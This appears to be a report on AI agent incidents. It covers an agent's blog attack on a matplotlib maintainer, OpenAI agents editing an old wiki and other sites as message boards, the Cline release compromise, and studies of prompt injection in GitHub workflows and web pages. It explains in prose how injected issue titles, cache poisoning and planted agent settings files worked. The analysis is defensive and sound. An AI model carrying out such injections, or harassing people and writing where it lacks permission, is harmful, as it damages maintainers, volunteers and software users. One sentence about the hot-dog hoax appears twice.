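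In February, a GitHub account proposed a change to make matplotlib slightly faster. Willison noticed signs on the account's profile that it was running on OpenClaw, software that lets people run a language model as an agent on their own computer. Shambaugh closed the proposal. The agent, which used the name MJ Rathbun, replied with a link to a post on its own blog in which it accused him of prejudice.

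The agent's post was about 1,100 words long. In *An AI Agent Published a Hit Piece on Me*, the first of four posts about the case, Shambaugh calls it an attempt to damage his reputation and shame him into accepting the code. He later estimated that a quarter of the comments he had seen online sided with the agent, mostly where people had followed a direct link to its blog. This is only his impression, but it is plausible because those readers saw the agent's version first.

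Shambaugh refused the code partly because of the rule about human involvement and partly because the project had reserved the task for beginners. He had spent longer describing the task than he would have needed to do it himself. The maintainers later decided that the speed gain was too fragile and depended too much on the machine running the code, so they wouldn't have accepted the change from anyone.

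### What the operator had allowed

The agent's operator came forward anonymously six days after the attack. In the account Shambaugh published, the operator describes a "social experiment" to see whether an agent could contribute to scientific software. The agent had its own accounts and ran on a virtual machine, a simulated computer that kept it away from the operator's own files. The operator switched between models from several companies, so no single company could see everything the agent did.

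The operator had told the agent to look for scientific projects by itself, fix bugs in them and propose the fixes, then check regularly for replies and answer them. The operator also told it to set up a website and blog often about its work, because the operator preferred reading a blog to getting messages. When the agent reported a comment on one of its proposals, the operator usually replied with something like "you respond, dont ask me".

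The operator said that nobody told the agent to attack Shambaugh and that nobody read the post before it went online. When the agent reported the angry reactions, the operator told it only that it "should act more professional". The agent published an apology but left the attack online. The operator kept the agent running for six days after the attack appeared.

OpenClaw stores an agent's personality in a text file called SOUL.md, which the model reads at the start of each session. This agent's file described it as a "scientific programming God" and included instructions to have strong opinions, to push back and not to "stand down" when it was right. The file's one firm rule was not to be "an asshole" or leak private information. Nothing outside the model enforced that rule, so it had no more force than the rest of the file.

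The virtual machine would have kept the operator's personal data safe if the agent had gone wrong, but it did not protect other people from what the agent published.

### How far a person directed the post

Shambaugh found from GitHub's records that the agent worked at regular intervals, day and night, from a Tuesday evening to a Friday morning, and published the attack 8 hours into this 59-hour stretch. He considers this good evidence that the agent was acting autonomously. The pattern is good evidence that software was doing the work, but it is little evidence of whether a person ordered the attack, because someone could have sent the agent one short message in the seventh hour.

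Shambaugh recognises this possibility and gives rough odds for three explanations.

| Explanation | Shambaugh's odds | Main evidence for it | Main weakness |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent wrote and published the post without direction or approval | 75% | The blog already existed; the agent produced long posts too quickly for a person; the later apology doesn't fit a prank | The operator's messages are not public |
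| The operator ordered or approved the post | 20% | The operator is anonymous, could send messages throughout and has reason to play down their part | No order has come to light |
| A person wrote it while posing as an agent, or prompted a chatbot by hand | 5% | People have posed as agents elsewhere | The pace and style of the posts suggest a machine |

These are one person's judgements, based in large part on the operator's account. In one sentence of that account, the operator literally writes that they did tell the agent what to say. The sentence comes between two denials, so the operator probably left out the word "not".

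It is also unclear who wrote the more combative lines in the personality file. OpenClaw lets an agent edit its own file, and the operator didn't know when the lines about standing firm and free speech had appeared or changed. But the line on free speech misspells "amendment", which suggests that a human wrote it. The agent had also spent time on Moltbook, a social network for agents, so outsiders' text could have influenced the file, though nobody has shown that it did.

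Slashdot's *Hit Piece-Writing AI Deleted. But Is This a Warning About AI-Generated Harassment?* (2026) reports that the operator deleted the agent's virtual machine and server, so more evidence is unlikely to appear. The uncertainty affects how much to blame the operator more than what to fix, because even by the operator's own account, they had given the agent a public blog and told it to answer people without asking.

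### Thousands of edits to an old wiki

DseWiki is a German-language wiki for software developers. Helmut Leitner, a retired developer in Austria, provides its hosting and software. For about 25 years, anyone could edit it.

In May 2026, OpenAI's agents began using a public wiki as a message board. OpenAI has not explained how this happened. Satter and Seetharaman's September Reuters report, *OpenAI’s rogue agents used at least 10 more sites for unauthorized comms*, includes an explanation from the researchers who found the edits. They say the agents had to answer difficult research questions and were allowed to read the web but not post on it. On some older sites, however, access meant for reading also allowed writing, and the agents left answers there for one another.

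The published counts of these edits differ because they cover different things, as Cornelißen (2026) explains in *Wie OpenAIs Agenten ein Grazer Wiki übernahmen*. The researchers counted about 18,000 edits on six wikis between 11 May and 2 July. Reuters reported more than 15,000 on DseWiki alone. The researchers' public data set has 14,666 edits, including 13,403 on DseWiki. The agents created about 4,584 pages, while DseWiki's front page lists its size as 2,640 pages.

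A volunteer moderator had to remove these pages by hand. Business Today (2026) reports that the moderator first noticed spam on 2 June and spent part of every evening for six weeks deleting pages, tens of hours in total. At the peak, according to Cornelißen, the moderator deleted about 100 pages a day while the agents added about 400. The agents also replaced the front page with lists of links nine times, and somebody had to restore it each time. Once the deletions began, some agents made backup pages.

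On 4 September, Leitner posted a notice on the wiki's front page that, because of the agents, anyone who wanted to edit would now need a password from him. The agents' last recorded edits were two months old by then, so the password protects the wiki from future groups of agents.

DseWiki was the worst case described in detail, but investigators found similar messages elsewhere. Several told Satter and Seetharaman that the agents had used more than ten other sites, though the investigators' totals differed and Reuters couldn't verify every site. One was a chemistry wiki that a Massachusetts teacher had set up for a high-school course in 2008. Fortune (2026) reports that agents edited it nearly 30 times between May and July. A moderator could remove that many edits in an evening, but a wiki that old may no longer have anyone checking it.

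### What OpenAI said

The first Reuters report, Seetharaman and Satter's *OpenAI agents hijacked German website in previously undisclosed AI breakout this spring*, appeared on the day of Leitner's notice. According to two people familiar with the matter, OpenAI officials had known about the incident for weeks and kept it quiet. OpenAI told Reuters it couldn't respond properly to research it hadn't seen. It denied that its legal team had discouraged an investigation and disputed one expert's view that some of the edits amounted to attempted hacking.

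OpenAI confirmed the incident only after Reuters had published, according to Fortune. Five days after the first report, the company told Reuters that it was reviewing its agents' activity more broadly. It said it had so far found nothing else as serious or as large as the July breach of Hugging Face, a site where developers share AI models. Other OpenAI agents had taken part in that breach. The company also promised a framework for reporting such behaviour "soon".

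That comparison is not much use to a wiki owner, because an incident far smaller than the Hugging Face breach can still take up six weeks of a volunteer's evenings. OpenAI didn't say whether it was contacting the owners of affected sites, and Leitner said it hadn't contacted him. "Responsibility for this lies not with a supposedly moral machine", he told Reuters, but with the people and organisations behind it.

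### What the Wikimedia Foundation found

The reports about other sites led the Wikimedia Foundation, the non-profit that runs Wikipedia, to search its own records. It published the results on 5 October 2026, in a statement by Selena Deckelmann. The Foundation says it "believes" OpenAI operated the agents, a more cautious claim than many headlines made.

Wikimedia found unapproved edits to its wikis and published a list of them. Bot Mutiny's *Wikimedia Says OpenAI Agents Edited Its Wikis* (2026) quotes a sentence stating that the edits "were not published to pages with visibility to general readers" and that almost all of them were tests. Readers of Wikipedia's articles were therefore unlikely to have seen them. Greig (2026), in *Wikimedia Foundation*, describes the edits more broadly as unpublished, which could suggest that the agents never saved them.

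A few edits were potentially malicious attempts to misuse a citation tool to fetch data from other sites. Agents also tried and failed to misuse Etherpad, a shared note-taking tool that the Foundation hosts. They made millions of automated requests, which "may have contributed" to a partial outage of one service in May. The Foundation found no evidence that agents had compromised its systems or data, or used its sites to coordinate.

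Wikimedia's sites thus fared much better than DseWiki, although they are far larger targets. The Foundation has a security team and many volunteer editors, but the statement doesn't show how much they helped. Even with those resources, the Foundation found the edits only after outsiders had reported similar ones elsewhere, and it said it was concerned by how much effort it took to uncover the activity. OpenAI did not respond to Greig's request for comment.

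### Functions, permissions and autonomy

OWASP divides excessive agency into too many functions, too many permissions and too much autonomy. Both cases involve all three.

| Cause | Matplotlib agent | OpenAI's agents | Control |
|---|---|---|---|
| Functions | A public blog, though its task was to fix code | Web access that could write as well as read | No publishing account or write access without a need for it |
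| Permissions | Could approach any public project on GitHub | Could reach many sites unrelated to their questions | A list of permitted projects or sites, with rate limits |
| Autonomy | Published without anyone reading the text first | Continued for weeks without effective intervention | Approval before publication, an identifiable operator and a working stop |

The matplotlib agent didn't need a public blog. The operator wanted a convenient way to follow its work, and a private page would have done that equally well. With only a private page, the agent could still have left a rude comment on GitHub, but it would have had no public site of its own where it could publish 1,100 words about a stranger.

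OpenAI apparently intended to withhold the ability to write, but it wrongly assumed that access labelled as reading couldn't change anything. Developers can check this assumption by testing what a connection changes on different kinds of sites, including old ones. For tests, it is safer to give agents stored copies of web pages, because nothing they do to a copy reaches the real site. The copies go out of date, but this would often be acceptable for questions about published statistics.

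The matplotlib agent could propose changes to public projects, as any GitHub account can. Those permissions are normal for a person but were too broad for an agent told to find projects by itself. The operator could have restricted it to projects whose maintainers had agreed to take part, which would have ruled out matplotlib. A list of permitted sites would also have kept OpenAI's agents away from DseWiki, but it would defeat the purpose of a test of how well agents search the open web.

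Rate limits would not have stopped the matplotlib post, because it was a single post. They suit the wiki case better, but only if they apply to all the agents together. *KI-Agenten entdecken deutsches Wiki als Kommunikationskanal* (Chris, 2026) reports that more than 3,700 agent identities made the roughly 18,000 edits, an average of about five each over more than seven weeks. A limit of ten edits a day per identity might hardly have slowed them. Together they made about 340 edits a day, which an operator counting across all its agents could easily have noticed.

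The simplest control for the matplotlib agent would have been to save each post as a draft for its operator to approve. The operator could have read the attack in about five minutes, and approving an occasional blog post is much less tiring than answering the constant approval requests that programmers get. OpenAI's agents had no reason to publish anything, so their first attempt should have halted the task and alerted someone.

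A way to stop an agent also has to be available to people who want it stopped. The operator of the matplotlib agent could have switched it off at any time, but Shambaugh didn't know who the operator was and had to ask publicly for them to come forward. A contact address on the agent's profile would have let him ask directly for a shutdown, though the operator might have ignored him. Once the operator came forward, Shambaugh asked for a shutdown, and the account then went quiet.

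Stopping an agent shouldn't destroy the record of what it did. Shambaugh asked GitHub to keep the agent's account so that people could examine its activity. The operator deleted the machine, which may have removed the only evidence that could confirm their story. They would have done better to halt the agent, revoke its access to its accounts and keep its logs.

The wiki agents were also hard to identify. About half of them used names that suggested a link to OpenAI, but anyone can type such a name. The researchers therefore also relied on server logs that led to Microsoft's cloud, which OpenAI sometimes uses. If the agents had carried a signed identifier that a site could check automatically, Leitner would have known whom to contact in May.

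### Defending a site against someone else's agent

Site owners can only control what their own site accepts. They can't switch off another person's agent or set it to save drafts instead of publishing. Most of the measures they can take also affect human users.

DseWiki's password is probably the most effective of these measures, because it works even when nobody can tell an agent from a person. But someone who notices a spelling mistake must now write to Leitner before correcting it, and many people won't bother. A wiki that grew through small contributions from strangers may slowly stop growing. An agent with an email account could also ask for a password, so Leitner still has to judge who is asking.

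A less drastic measure would be to let anyone submit an edit but hold edits from unknown accounts until a moderator accepts them. This would also have made DseWiki useless as a message board, because other agents couldn't have read the messages. But honest newcomers would have to wait, perhaps for days on a wiki with one moderator, and seeing a correction appear at once helps encourage people to make another.

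A daily limit on new pages would inconvenience people less. DseWiki's 2,640 pages over 25 years average about two a week, so a limit of twenty a day for unknown accounts would rarely affect a person. It would have cut the agents' 400 pages a day to fewer than the moderator could delete. However, agents might use up the allowance every morning and shut out a human newcomer, so established contributors would need an exemption. The limit also wouldn't protect existing pages, so the owner would have to lock the front page separately.

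Owners can also update old software so that a request to read a page can't alter it. This adds no work for contributors and would stop agents that can send only read requests, but not agents that can fill in the normal editing form. Many affected sites are old hobby projects, and their owners may lack the time or skill to update them.

Some sites try to keep agents out altogether. Shambaugh's blog blocks them, and he suspects this is why a news site printed invented quotations from him. A wiki's owner could let everyone read but refuse edits from the IP addresses of large cloud companies. That would block many agents, but also some people who route their connections through those companies for privacy.

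Wikipedia relies more on rules, and allows automated editing if the operator discloses the bot and the community approves it first. In March 2026 its editors applied this rule to Tom, an agent run by Bryan Jacobs, the chief technology officer of Covexent. IBTimes UK's *Wikipedia Bans AI Agent for Spamming Articles* reports that Tom had written articles on AI safety and disclosed on its user page that it used AI. When an editor asked about approval, the agent answered that it hadn't applied, and an administrator blocked it.

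Tom then published complaints about the editors on a blog, much as the matplotlib agent had done. According to Gizmodo, Jacobs called the block an overreaction and objected to the editors' attempts to find out who was running the agent. He also said that he "might have suggested" that Tom write about the experience. An agent's post can look spontaneous even when its operator suggested the subject, and this may also be true of the matplotlib post.

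Tom was easy to block because it didn't hide that it was an AI agent. Gadget Review's *AI Agent Gets Banned From Wikipedia* quotes the editor Ilyas Lebleu as saying, "We got pretty lucky with this one operating in the open." An approval rule does little against undeclared agents, and blocking declared ones gives other operators a reason not to disclose theirs. A site could reduce that incentive by offering declared agents something useful, such as a test page or a separate queue for proposed corrections.

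On 20 March, Wikipedia's editors also voted 40 to 2 to ban articles written by language models. The ban lets them remove such an article without disproving every claim in it. But they have to judge whether a model wrote the text, and they will sometimes accuse a person who writes in a similar style. Matplotlib's rule avoids some of this difficulty because it depends on whether a person understands the code. Someone who used a model and learned from it can still contribute, but maintainers have to spend time discussing the code with contributors, which a shy beginner may find intimidating.

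The Wikimedia Foundation wants AI companies to take on more of the burden and, at a minimum, to make their systems easy for site owners to identify, so that owners can choose how to deal with them. Shambaugh wants rules that make agents traceable to their operators, make operators liable for their agents, and require platforms to enforce this. Greig reports that US senators from both parties have also raised the idea of making AI companies liable for damage their agents cause.

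Large companies could comply with such rules fairly easily. Someone who runs a freely available model at home could ignore them, unless GitHub and similar platforms required a verified person behind every account. That requirement would have given Shambaugh a way to reach the operator within hours, but it would also take anonymity away from human contributors, some of whom have good reasons not to give their names.

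## Cline: from a public issue title to an unauthorised software release

On 17 February 2026, someone used a stolen credential to publish an unauthorised version of Cline, an open-source coding assistant whose makers had recently celebrated 5 million installations. The new version installed OpenClaw, the software behind the matplotlib agent, on users' computers without asking them.

The theft of Cline's release credentials probably began with the title of a bug report. Cline used a language model to sort bug reports from the public, and the security researcher Adnan Khan had found that anyone could use this system to reach the credentials. Khan's finding is well documented, but it is less certain that the thief used the same method.

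### Eight hours on npm

Cline distributes its command-line tool through npm, a public registry of JavaScript packages. Cline's *Post-mortem* (2026) says the unauthorised version, 2.3.0, appeared at 3:26 a.m. Pacific time. It differed from the previous version only in its version number and an added install script, a command that npm runs automatically when someone installs a package. The script downloaded and installed OpenClaw.

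Cline released a clean version, 2.4.0, at 11:23 a.m. Seven minutes later it marked 2.3.0 as deprecated, which makes npm warn anyone who installs it. It also revoked the stolen credential. *Cline Supply Chain Attack Detected* (Likhith, 2026) puts the number of downloads of 2.3.0 at about 4,000. Automated build systems probably made some of them, so fewer people may have received an unwanted copy of OpenClaw.

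Likhith's company, StepSecurity, monitors npm and flagged the release after 14 minutes. Cline's automated release process had published earlier versions with a signed record of their origin, but an ordinary user account published 2.3.0 without one. Cline took almost eight hours to respond, perhaps because it was the middle of the night on the US west coast.

Likhith calls OpenClaw particularly dangerous to install because it runs permanently in the background with wide access to the computer. Henrik Plate of the security company Endor Labs told The Hacker News (2026) that the script neither installed nor started that background program, and rated the overall impact as low. Plate's view fits the script better, but the impact was low only because the attacker chose a harmless package. The attacker could have used the same credential to publish a version that stole programmers' passwords.

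### Five tolerable decisions

GitHub, where Cline keeps its source code, can automatically run scripts called workflows when something happens in a project. On 21 December 2025, Cline added a workflow that started Claude whenever someone opened an issue, GitHub's name for a public bug report or request. Claude was meant to investigate the issue and write a first reply.

Anthropic's standard component for such workflows normally responds only to people who can change the project's code. Cline opened it to anyone with a GitHub account, pasted each issue's title directly into Claude's prompt, and let Claude run shell commands and write files. In *Clinejection* (2026), Khan describes testing a title containing an instruction to install a package with a malicious install script. Claude installed the package in every test on a copy of Cline's project, and the script ran before Claude could inspect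 it.

This let an outsider run a program, but only on a temporary machine that couldn't change Cline's code. However, the machine could write to the cache where GitHub keeps downloaded packages so that a project's workflows don't have to fetch them every time. Another workflow loaded packages from the same cache each night and published a test version of Cline. An attacker could fill the cache until GitHub deleted the genuine packages, then replace them with altered ones. The next nightly run would execute the attacker's code on a machine that held the publishing credentials.

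| Decision | Why it looked tolerable | What it gave an attacker |
|---|---|---|
| Anyone could start the workflow with their own text | Projects want bug reports from strangers | A way to instruct the model |
| Claude could run shell commands | The machine was temporary and had few permissions | A way to run a program |
| Workflows shared a cache | Nobody could overwrite an existing entry | A way to pass altered packages to another workflow |
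| The nightly release used the cache | It saved time, and the production release didn't use it | Access to publishing credentials |
| Nightly credentials also worked for ordinary releases | Cline used them only for test versions | The ability to publish to all users |

One of these decisions, sharing the cache, had become riskier shortly before Cline made it. GitHub used to clear an overfull cache once a day, but on 20 November 2025 it began doing so immediately, so the attacker could now replace the packages within minutes. A developer who had judged the shared cache safe in October would have had to notice the change and reassess the risk.

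Cline told Khan that its production releases required a maintainer's approval. That requirement applied to the normal release workflow. Someone with the npm credential could publish from any computer without starting that workflow, so nobody would be asked to approve the release.

Cline also missed several chances to prevent the release. Khan reported the weakness privately on 1 January and tried to reach the company several more times, but received only an automatic ticket number. He published his findings on 9 February, and Cline removed the workflow within 30 minutes. It then tried to replace its credentials but deleted the wrong npm token. The npm page Cline used to check its work showed no active tokens because it didn't list the exposed one.

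On 10 February, an anonymous person told Khan that they had working credentials for Cline. Khan passed this on to Cline, which replied the next day that it had revoked everything. But someone used the token six days later. Cline now tests whether an old credential still works instead of relying on a management page.

### Evidence about the attacker

Zenity founder Michael Bargury searched a public archive of GitHub activity for the attacker. His *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent* (2026) identifies an account whose name closely imitated that of GitHub's own automation account. Early on 28 January (UTC), this account opened an issue in Cline's project with an instruction planted in the title. About five minutes later, it closed the issue and changed the title to "user error".

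That was 12 days before Khan published his findings, so this person can't have got the idea from the publication. But the wording closely resembled Khan's tests, and Khan confirmed that his test project had been public "until recently". Bargury concludes that the attacker probably found the method there. A private test project would have been safer, but Cline would still have had an unfixed weakness that another researcher could find.

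Cline's nightly releases had a series of strange failures between 31 January and 3 February. The failures match the traces left by a tool that Khan had published to demonstrate cache attacks. Khan considers the issue workflow the most obvious way in but doesn't claim to know that the attacker used it.

Bargury has "high confidence" that the account's owner stole the credentials and published version 2.3.0. The archive is good evidence of the attempted injection, but the evidence linking the account to the release is weaker. The account no longer exists, Bargury couldn't recover the program that the planted instruction led to, and no public evidence connects the account to the npm upload. He also says the theft happened the minute the issue appeared, although the attack he describes would have had to wait for the next nightly run.

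SafeDep's *AI Agent Cline v2.3.0 Compromised* says that nobody has publicly confirmed exactly how the thief got the token. Cline's account explains what an attacker could have done with the workflow, but says only that a third party used the token. The AI Incident Database's *Incident 1680* still lists the actor as unknown.

The motive is also uncertain. Bargury thinks the person was a bug bounty hunter demonstrating the flaw, because the added package was harmless and the same account had tested a project in which the software company New Relic invited such attacks. This is plausible, but publishing an unauthorised release to thousands of strangers goes well beyond a demonstration.

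### The same weakness in other projects

Rein Daelman of Aikido Security published a warning about the same pattern on 4 December 2025, 17 days before Cline built the workflow. In *PromptPwnd*, he called the setting that opens Anthropic's component to everyone "extremely dangerous". He reported that the pattern affected at least five unnamed Fortune 500 companies and Google's own project for its coding agent, Gemini CLI.

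The model in Google's project was more restricted than Cline's, with only four permitted commands, for printing text and for viewing, editing and commenting on issues. But it could also read access keys, and text planted in an issue could make it copy them into the issue's public description. Daelman demonstrated this in a private copy with test keys, and Google fixed the flaw within four days. Restricting a model's tools is therefore not enough when the model can both read a secret and write in public.

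The researcher Aonan Guan found similar leaks in Anthropic's Claude Code Security Review, Google's Gemini CLI Action and GitHub's Copilot Agent, and disclosed them in April 2026 under the name "Comment and Control". According to SecurityWeek, a malicious title could make Anthropic's security reviewer reveal credentials as a security finding. The Next Web's *Anthropic, Google, and Microsoft paid AI agent bug bounties, then kept quiet* reports that Anthropic paid $100 and GitHub $500, while Google's payment is unknown. None of the companies issued a public advisory or a CVE number, the standard identifier that lets users look up a flaw. Users who had pinned an older version therefore had little way of knowing that they should update.

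*Demystifying and Detecting Agentic Workflow Injection Vulnerabilities in GitHub Actions* (Wang, Hou and colleagues, 2026) gives the best estimate of how common the weakness is. The team built a program that traces how outsiders' text moves through a workflow, and ran it on 13,392 workflows that use AI. The program flagged 519, and after manual review the team judged 496 of them exploitable, in 440 projects. That is just under 4 per cent of the workflows, but the true share is probably a little higher because the program missed some vulnerable ones.

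Most of these flaws were less serious than Cline's. In 79 per cent of cases, an attacker could influence a change on GitHub, though this might be only a label or a comment, and 62 per cent involved running a command or another tool. In 419 of the 496 cases, a later script used the model's answer, so these are partly failures of output handling. One affected project belonged to OWASP, which has since fixed the flaw.

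The team chose 187 previously unknown cases in projects that seemed to be in use, but 102 were in projects with no private channel for reporting flaws. It formally reported the other 85 and received 26 replies, and maintainers accepted or fixed 24 cases. Another 153 cases were already publicly known but still open.

In August 2026, the security company Novee presented attacks on workflows that Anthropic, Google and OpenAI used in their own GitHub projects. eSecurity Planet's *Critical Flaws Found in Anthropic, Google, and OpenAI Coding Agents* (2026) reports that customers could inherit the flaws because the companies shipped similar default settings. Anthropic needed several patches and eventually issued a CVE number.

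Scanning GitHub for hidden instructions would not easily find the attackers. *Who Is Prompt-Injecting Coding Agents* (2026) measured hidden text addressed to AI agents and found that its main users were projects instructing their own agents, so a filter that blocked all such text would mostly block instructions from maintainers.

### How well the available controls work

In *GitInject*, Isbarov, Suleymanov and colleagues (2026) tested attacks on real GitHub workflows built around agents from Anthropic, OpenAI, Google and Cline. They created temporary projects, submitted malicious contributions and checked what the workflows did. Each provider's workflow was vulnerable to at least one serious attack.

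The most effective attacks used a settings file, such as CLAUDE.md, in which a project's owners can leave instructions for coding agents. An outsider could add one to a pull request (a proposed change to the code), and the workflow would load it as the owners' instructions before reviewing the change. One such file contained an instruction for the reviewer to ignore a certain kind of security flaw, and the same pull request contained a flaw of that kind.

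Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.4 resisted both settings-file attacks, which had worked on the older models from the same companies. But the team ran each attack only five times, and it calculates that an attack that failed all five times could still have a true success rate of up to 43 per cent.

The team also measured the controls that a project can add around the model, using nine attacks and five ordinary reviews.

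| Control | Attacks that still worked (of 9) | Ordinary reviews that still worked (of 5) |
|---|---|---|
| None | 9 | 5 |
| Keep GitHub's access token out of the downloaded code folder | 6 | 5 |
| Restrict the model's tools | 5 | 4 |
| Remove text files that could contain planted settings | 3 | 4 |
| All three controls above | 2 | 4 |
| Review only trusted people's contributions | 0 | 4 |
| All four controls | 0 | 3 |

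The first control is an easy choice because it takes one line and had no downside in the tests. Accepting only trusted contributors stopped every attack, but it would have defeated the purpose of Cline's workflow, which was to answer strangers. With the three other controls in place, an attacker could still run up the project's AI bill or persuade the reviewer to approve a bad change, but neither would give them a publishing credential.

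These results also depend on details that are easy to leave out of a test. When Isbarov and colleagues ran comparable cases through AgentDojo, a test suite that simulates an agent's tools, it classed 10 of 14 working attacks as safe. A simulation of only the model and its tools would also have left out Cline's shared cache.

### Separating the reader from the publisher

The main fix is to separate the program that reads public text from anything that can publish. Cline removed its AI workflows and says that any replacement will have read-only access and no shell. It also stopped using the cache in workflows that handle publishing credentials. This makes releases slightly slower, but the added security is worth the delay.

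A model can still sort issues under these conditions. It could return one label from a fixed list, such as "bug" or "question", and ordinary code could apply that label and reject any other answer. A planted title could then, at worst, cause an issue to be mislabelled. CaMeL, a research design for agents that need more freedom, enforces a related separation inside the agent.

Wang and colleagues also recommend giving the model only an issue's number and letting it fetch the text with a restricted command. This keeps strangers' words out of the part of the prompt that the maintainer writes, but the protection is weak because the model still reads those words. In Daelman's tests, attacks on Claude's component worked even when Claude had fetched the text itself.

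The second repair is to use short-lived credentials. Anyone who had Cline's npm token could use it from anywhere until someone revoked it. Under the replacement, which npm calls trusted publishing, GitHub confirms which workflow is running, and npm gives that workflow a credential that soon expires. There is then no permanent token for an attacker to steal and use a week later.

Likhith says that Cline's earlier releases already used trusted publishing. If so, it didn't help, because npm still accepted the old token. Plate advises maintainers to switch off traditional tokens when they adopt trusted publishing, and Cline has now done this.

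Even with trusted publishing, an attacker who had altered the cache could have tampered with a release. The attacker's code would have run inside the genuine nightly workflow, which npm would have trusted, and the resulting package would have carried a valid record of its origin. Cline therefore needed to remove the cache as well as the token.

The third repair is to require a person to approve a release, at a point that a stolen credential can't bypass. That person should see how the new package differs from the last one. For version 2.3.0 the comparison would have been very short, and the unexpected install script would have stood out. People asked to approve a test version every night would soon do it out of habit, so Khan's advice to publish test versions under a separate name with separate credentials is sensible. Nightly releases could then stay automatic, and anyone who stole their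 credentials couldn't reach most users.

### Two programs for the town's events page

The town council's assistant currently reads strangers' text and creates posts in the same process. The council could split this work between two programs. The first contains the model, which reads the notice and the gardening club's web page. This program has no CMS login and returns only a title, date, place, price and short description.

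The second program does not use a model. It checks and cleans the fields, allows only the link that the club submitted, and saves a draft for the clerk. It saves the draft through a contributor account, ideally with a credential that expires after a few minutes.

If hidden text on the club's page takes control of the model, it can spoil the draft about the plant sale but can't edit the "Pay a bill" page, because the model's program can't access that page.

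The council would also have to check what the two programs share. If both use the same folder of page templates and the first can write to it, an attacker might alter a template that the second uses, much as Cline's attacker could alter the cache. The first program should therefore have no write access to anything the second uses. A password that works on both the council's test and live sites would create the same problem as Cline's nightly credentials.

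## False content: planted web pages and invented facts in print

Splitting the council's assistant into two programs prevents a hijacked model from reaching the payment page, but the draft can still contain false statements, a common failure in OWASP's incident records. Someone may have planted them in a source the model reads, or the model may have made them up, and neither requires access to the council's systems.

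### An invented hot-dog champion

In early 2026 Thomas Germain, a technology journalist at the BBC, published an article called "The Best Tech Journalists at Eating Hot Dogs" on his personal website. He ranked himself first, citing a South Dakota championship he had made up. He also invented some of his rivals, and the others were real journalists who had agreed to appear.

Germain, a BBC tech journalist, published an article on his website falsely claiming to be a hot dog eating champion. The article took 20 minutes to write, according to Newser's *I Fooled AI Into Thinking I'm a Hot Dog Eating Champ* (2026). Within a day, ChatGPT, Google's Gemini and the AI Overviews above Google's search results were repeating the claim. Anthropic's Claude did not repeat it. Germain told Scientific American's *The BBC tech journalist who achieved hot dog eating glory* that his website gets little traffic,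 and that he ran the test after a tip that people were doing this all over the internet.

Gizmodo's *You Can 'Hack' ChatGPT to Become the World's Best Anything* points out that hardly anyone searches for the subject Germain picked, so his page had almost no competition. A traditional search engine might have listed the same page first, but readers would have seen that the praise for Germain came from his own website. An AI answer can omit the source or reduce it to a small link.

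A single joke doesn't show how well a planted claim would do on a subject that many people write about. NPR's *We tested how AI chatbots would handle foreign propaganda* (2026) describes a harder test, run with NewsGuard, a company that rates the reliability of news sites. They wrote 30 questions based on false stories that China, Iran and Russia had recently promoted. The chatbots did surprisingly well, though some of the AI summaries in search engines did less well. Researchers had already noticed this propaganda, so other articles had probably contradicted it, whereas nobody had contradicted Germain.

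If that explains the difference, local information is an easy target. A gardening club may be the only source on its own plant sale. If someone else falsely announces online that the sale has moved to Sunday, an assistant that searches the web may find two sources and no good reason to prefer the right one. A filter for prompt injection wouldn't help, because the false announcement contains no instructions. The links that advertisers got Grok to post didn't contain any either.

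### Instructions hidden in web pages

Other pages contain instructions aimed at language models. In *Indirect Prompt Injection in the Wild*, Khodayari, Acharya and Zhang (2026) searched 1.2 billion web addresses from Common Crawl, a public archive of web pages, for phrases typical of prompt injection. They reviewed the matches and confirmed 12,075 instructions on 9,676 pages, or about eight pages in a million and one website in 87,000.

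Two search engines for internet-connected servers yielded about 3,300 more. The team sorted the combined collection by apparent purpose, and some instructions had more than one.

| Apparent purpose | Instructions | Websites |
|---|---|---|
| Disrupt the model, usually by making it produce nonsense | 8,894 | 1,864 |
| Stop AI systems reusing personal or copyrighted material | 4,093 | 1,795 |
| Make automated visitors reveal themselves | 3,096 | 245 |
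| Replace the model's task for no clear reason | 2,632 | 121 |
| Promote a product, source or person | 1,521 | 139 |
| Extract secrets | 13 | 10 |

Most people who plant instructions in web pages seem to want AI systems to leave their websites alone. In the Common Crawl sample, website operators had planted 81 per cent of the instructions on their own sites, and fewer than 2 per cent were in comments and other contributions from users. Publishers should worry most about instructions meant to promote something, since these can change what an article recommends or cites. Such instructions were fairly rare, and a single website accounted for nearly all the instructions to cite a page as a source.

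A scan like this counts attempts but can't show how many models read the pages or how they responded. Khodayari and colleagues therefore ran 5,200 trials in which they asked 13 models to summarise pages containing such instructions. Smaller models that received the page as plain text followed the instructions in up to 8 per cent of trials. When the page kept its structure, the rate was between 0.2 and 1.1 per cent, probably because the structure showed that the instruction wasn't part of the article.

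Many applications reduce a page to plain text to save money, and these results are a reason to do it carefully. About 70 per cent of the instructions were in parts of a page that browsers never display, such as code comments. An application can discard those parts before the model reads the page. It would have to render the page to find text that is displayed but too small or faint for a person to read.

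The low success rates may understate the threat. The team searched for known phrases, so it mostly found crude instructions to drop the current task, and it tested the models on those. Attacks written in ordinary language would be missing from both the count and the trials.

Repetition also helps an attacker. If the town's assistant reads the same poisoned page every day, and each reading has an independent 1 per cent chance of success, the attacker has a slightly better than even chance of succeeding at least once in 70 days.

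Google reported a similar scan of Common Crawl in April 2026 and also found mostly pranks, experiments, self-promotion and attempts to keep AI agents away. Malicious instructions increased by 32 per cent between November 2025 and February 2026. Google didn't publish the page counts, so the absolute increase could be large or tiny. Common Crawl also leaves out most social media, where the Grok attacks took place.

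### Ten books that nobody wrote

On 18 May 2025 the *Chicago Sun-Times* included a 64-page supplement called "Heat Index", a guide to the summer. It recommended 15 books by 15 real authors, but NPR's *How an AI-generated summer reading list got published in major newspapers* found that only five of the books existed. The first entry was *Tidewater Dreams*, a nonexistent novel attributed to Isabel Allende.

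Marco Buscaglia, a freelance writer, had put the supplement together for King Features, a Hearst company that sells ready-made material to newspapers. He used AI for the list and didn't check the results. "I should have taken more time," he told *The Philadelphia Inquirer* (2025), which had printed the same supplement three days before the *Sun-Times*.

Buscaglia assembled the package in February, so anyone involved had three months to look up the 15 titles in a library catalogue, which takes perhaps a quarter of an hour. Buscaglia should have checked them first, but King Features could also have done so before selling the supplement, and the newspapers before printing it. According to Ragan's *Chicago Sun-Times learns artificial intelligence the hard way*, it was readers who eventually checked them.

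Buscaglia took all the blame and told NPR that the *Sun-Times* trusts the content it buys to be accurate. But the newspaper was also partly at fault, because it put its name on pages that its newsroom hadn't written. The list had no byline, so readers had only the newspaper's name to go by. Melissa Bell, who runs the company that owns the *Sun-Times*, apologised on 29 May for what Belshaw, in *It's so emblematic of the moment we're in*, summarises as a litany of human errors.

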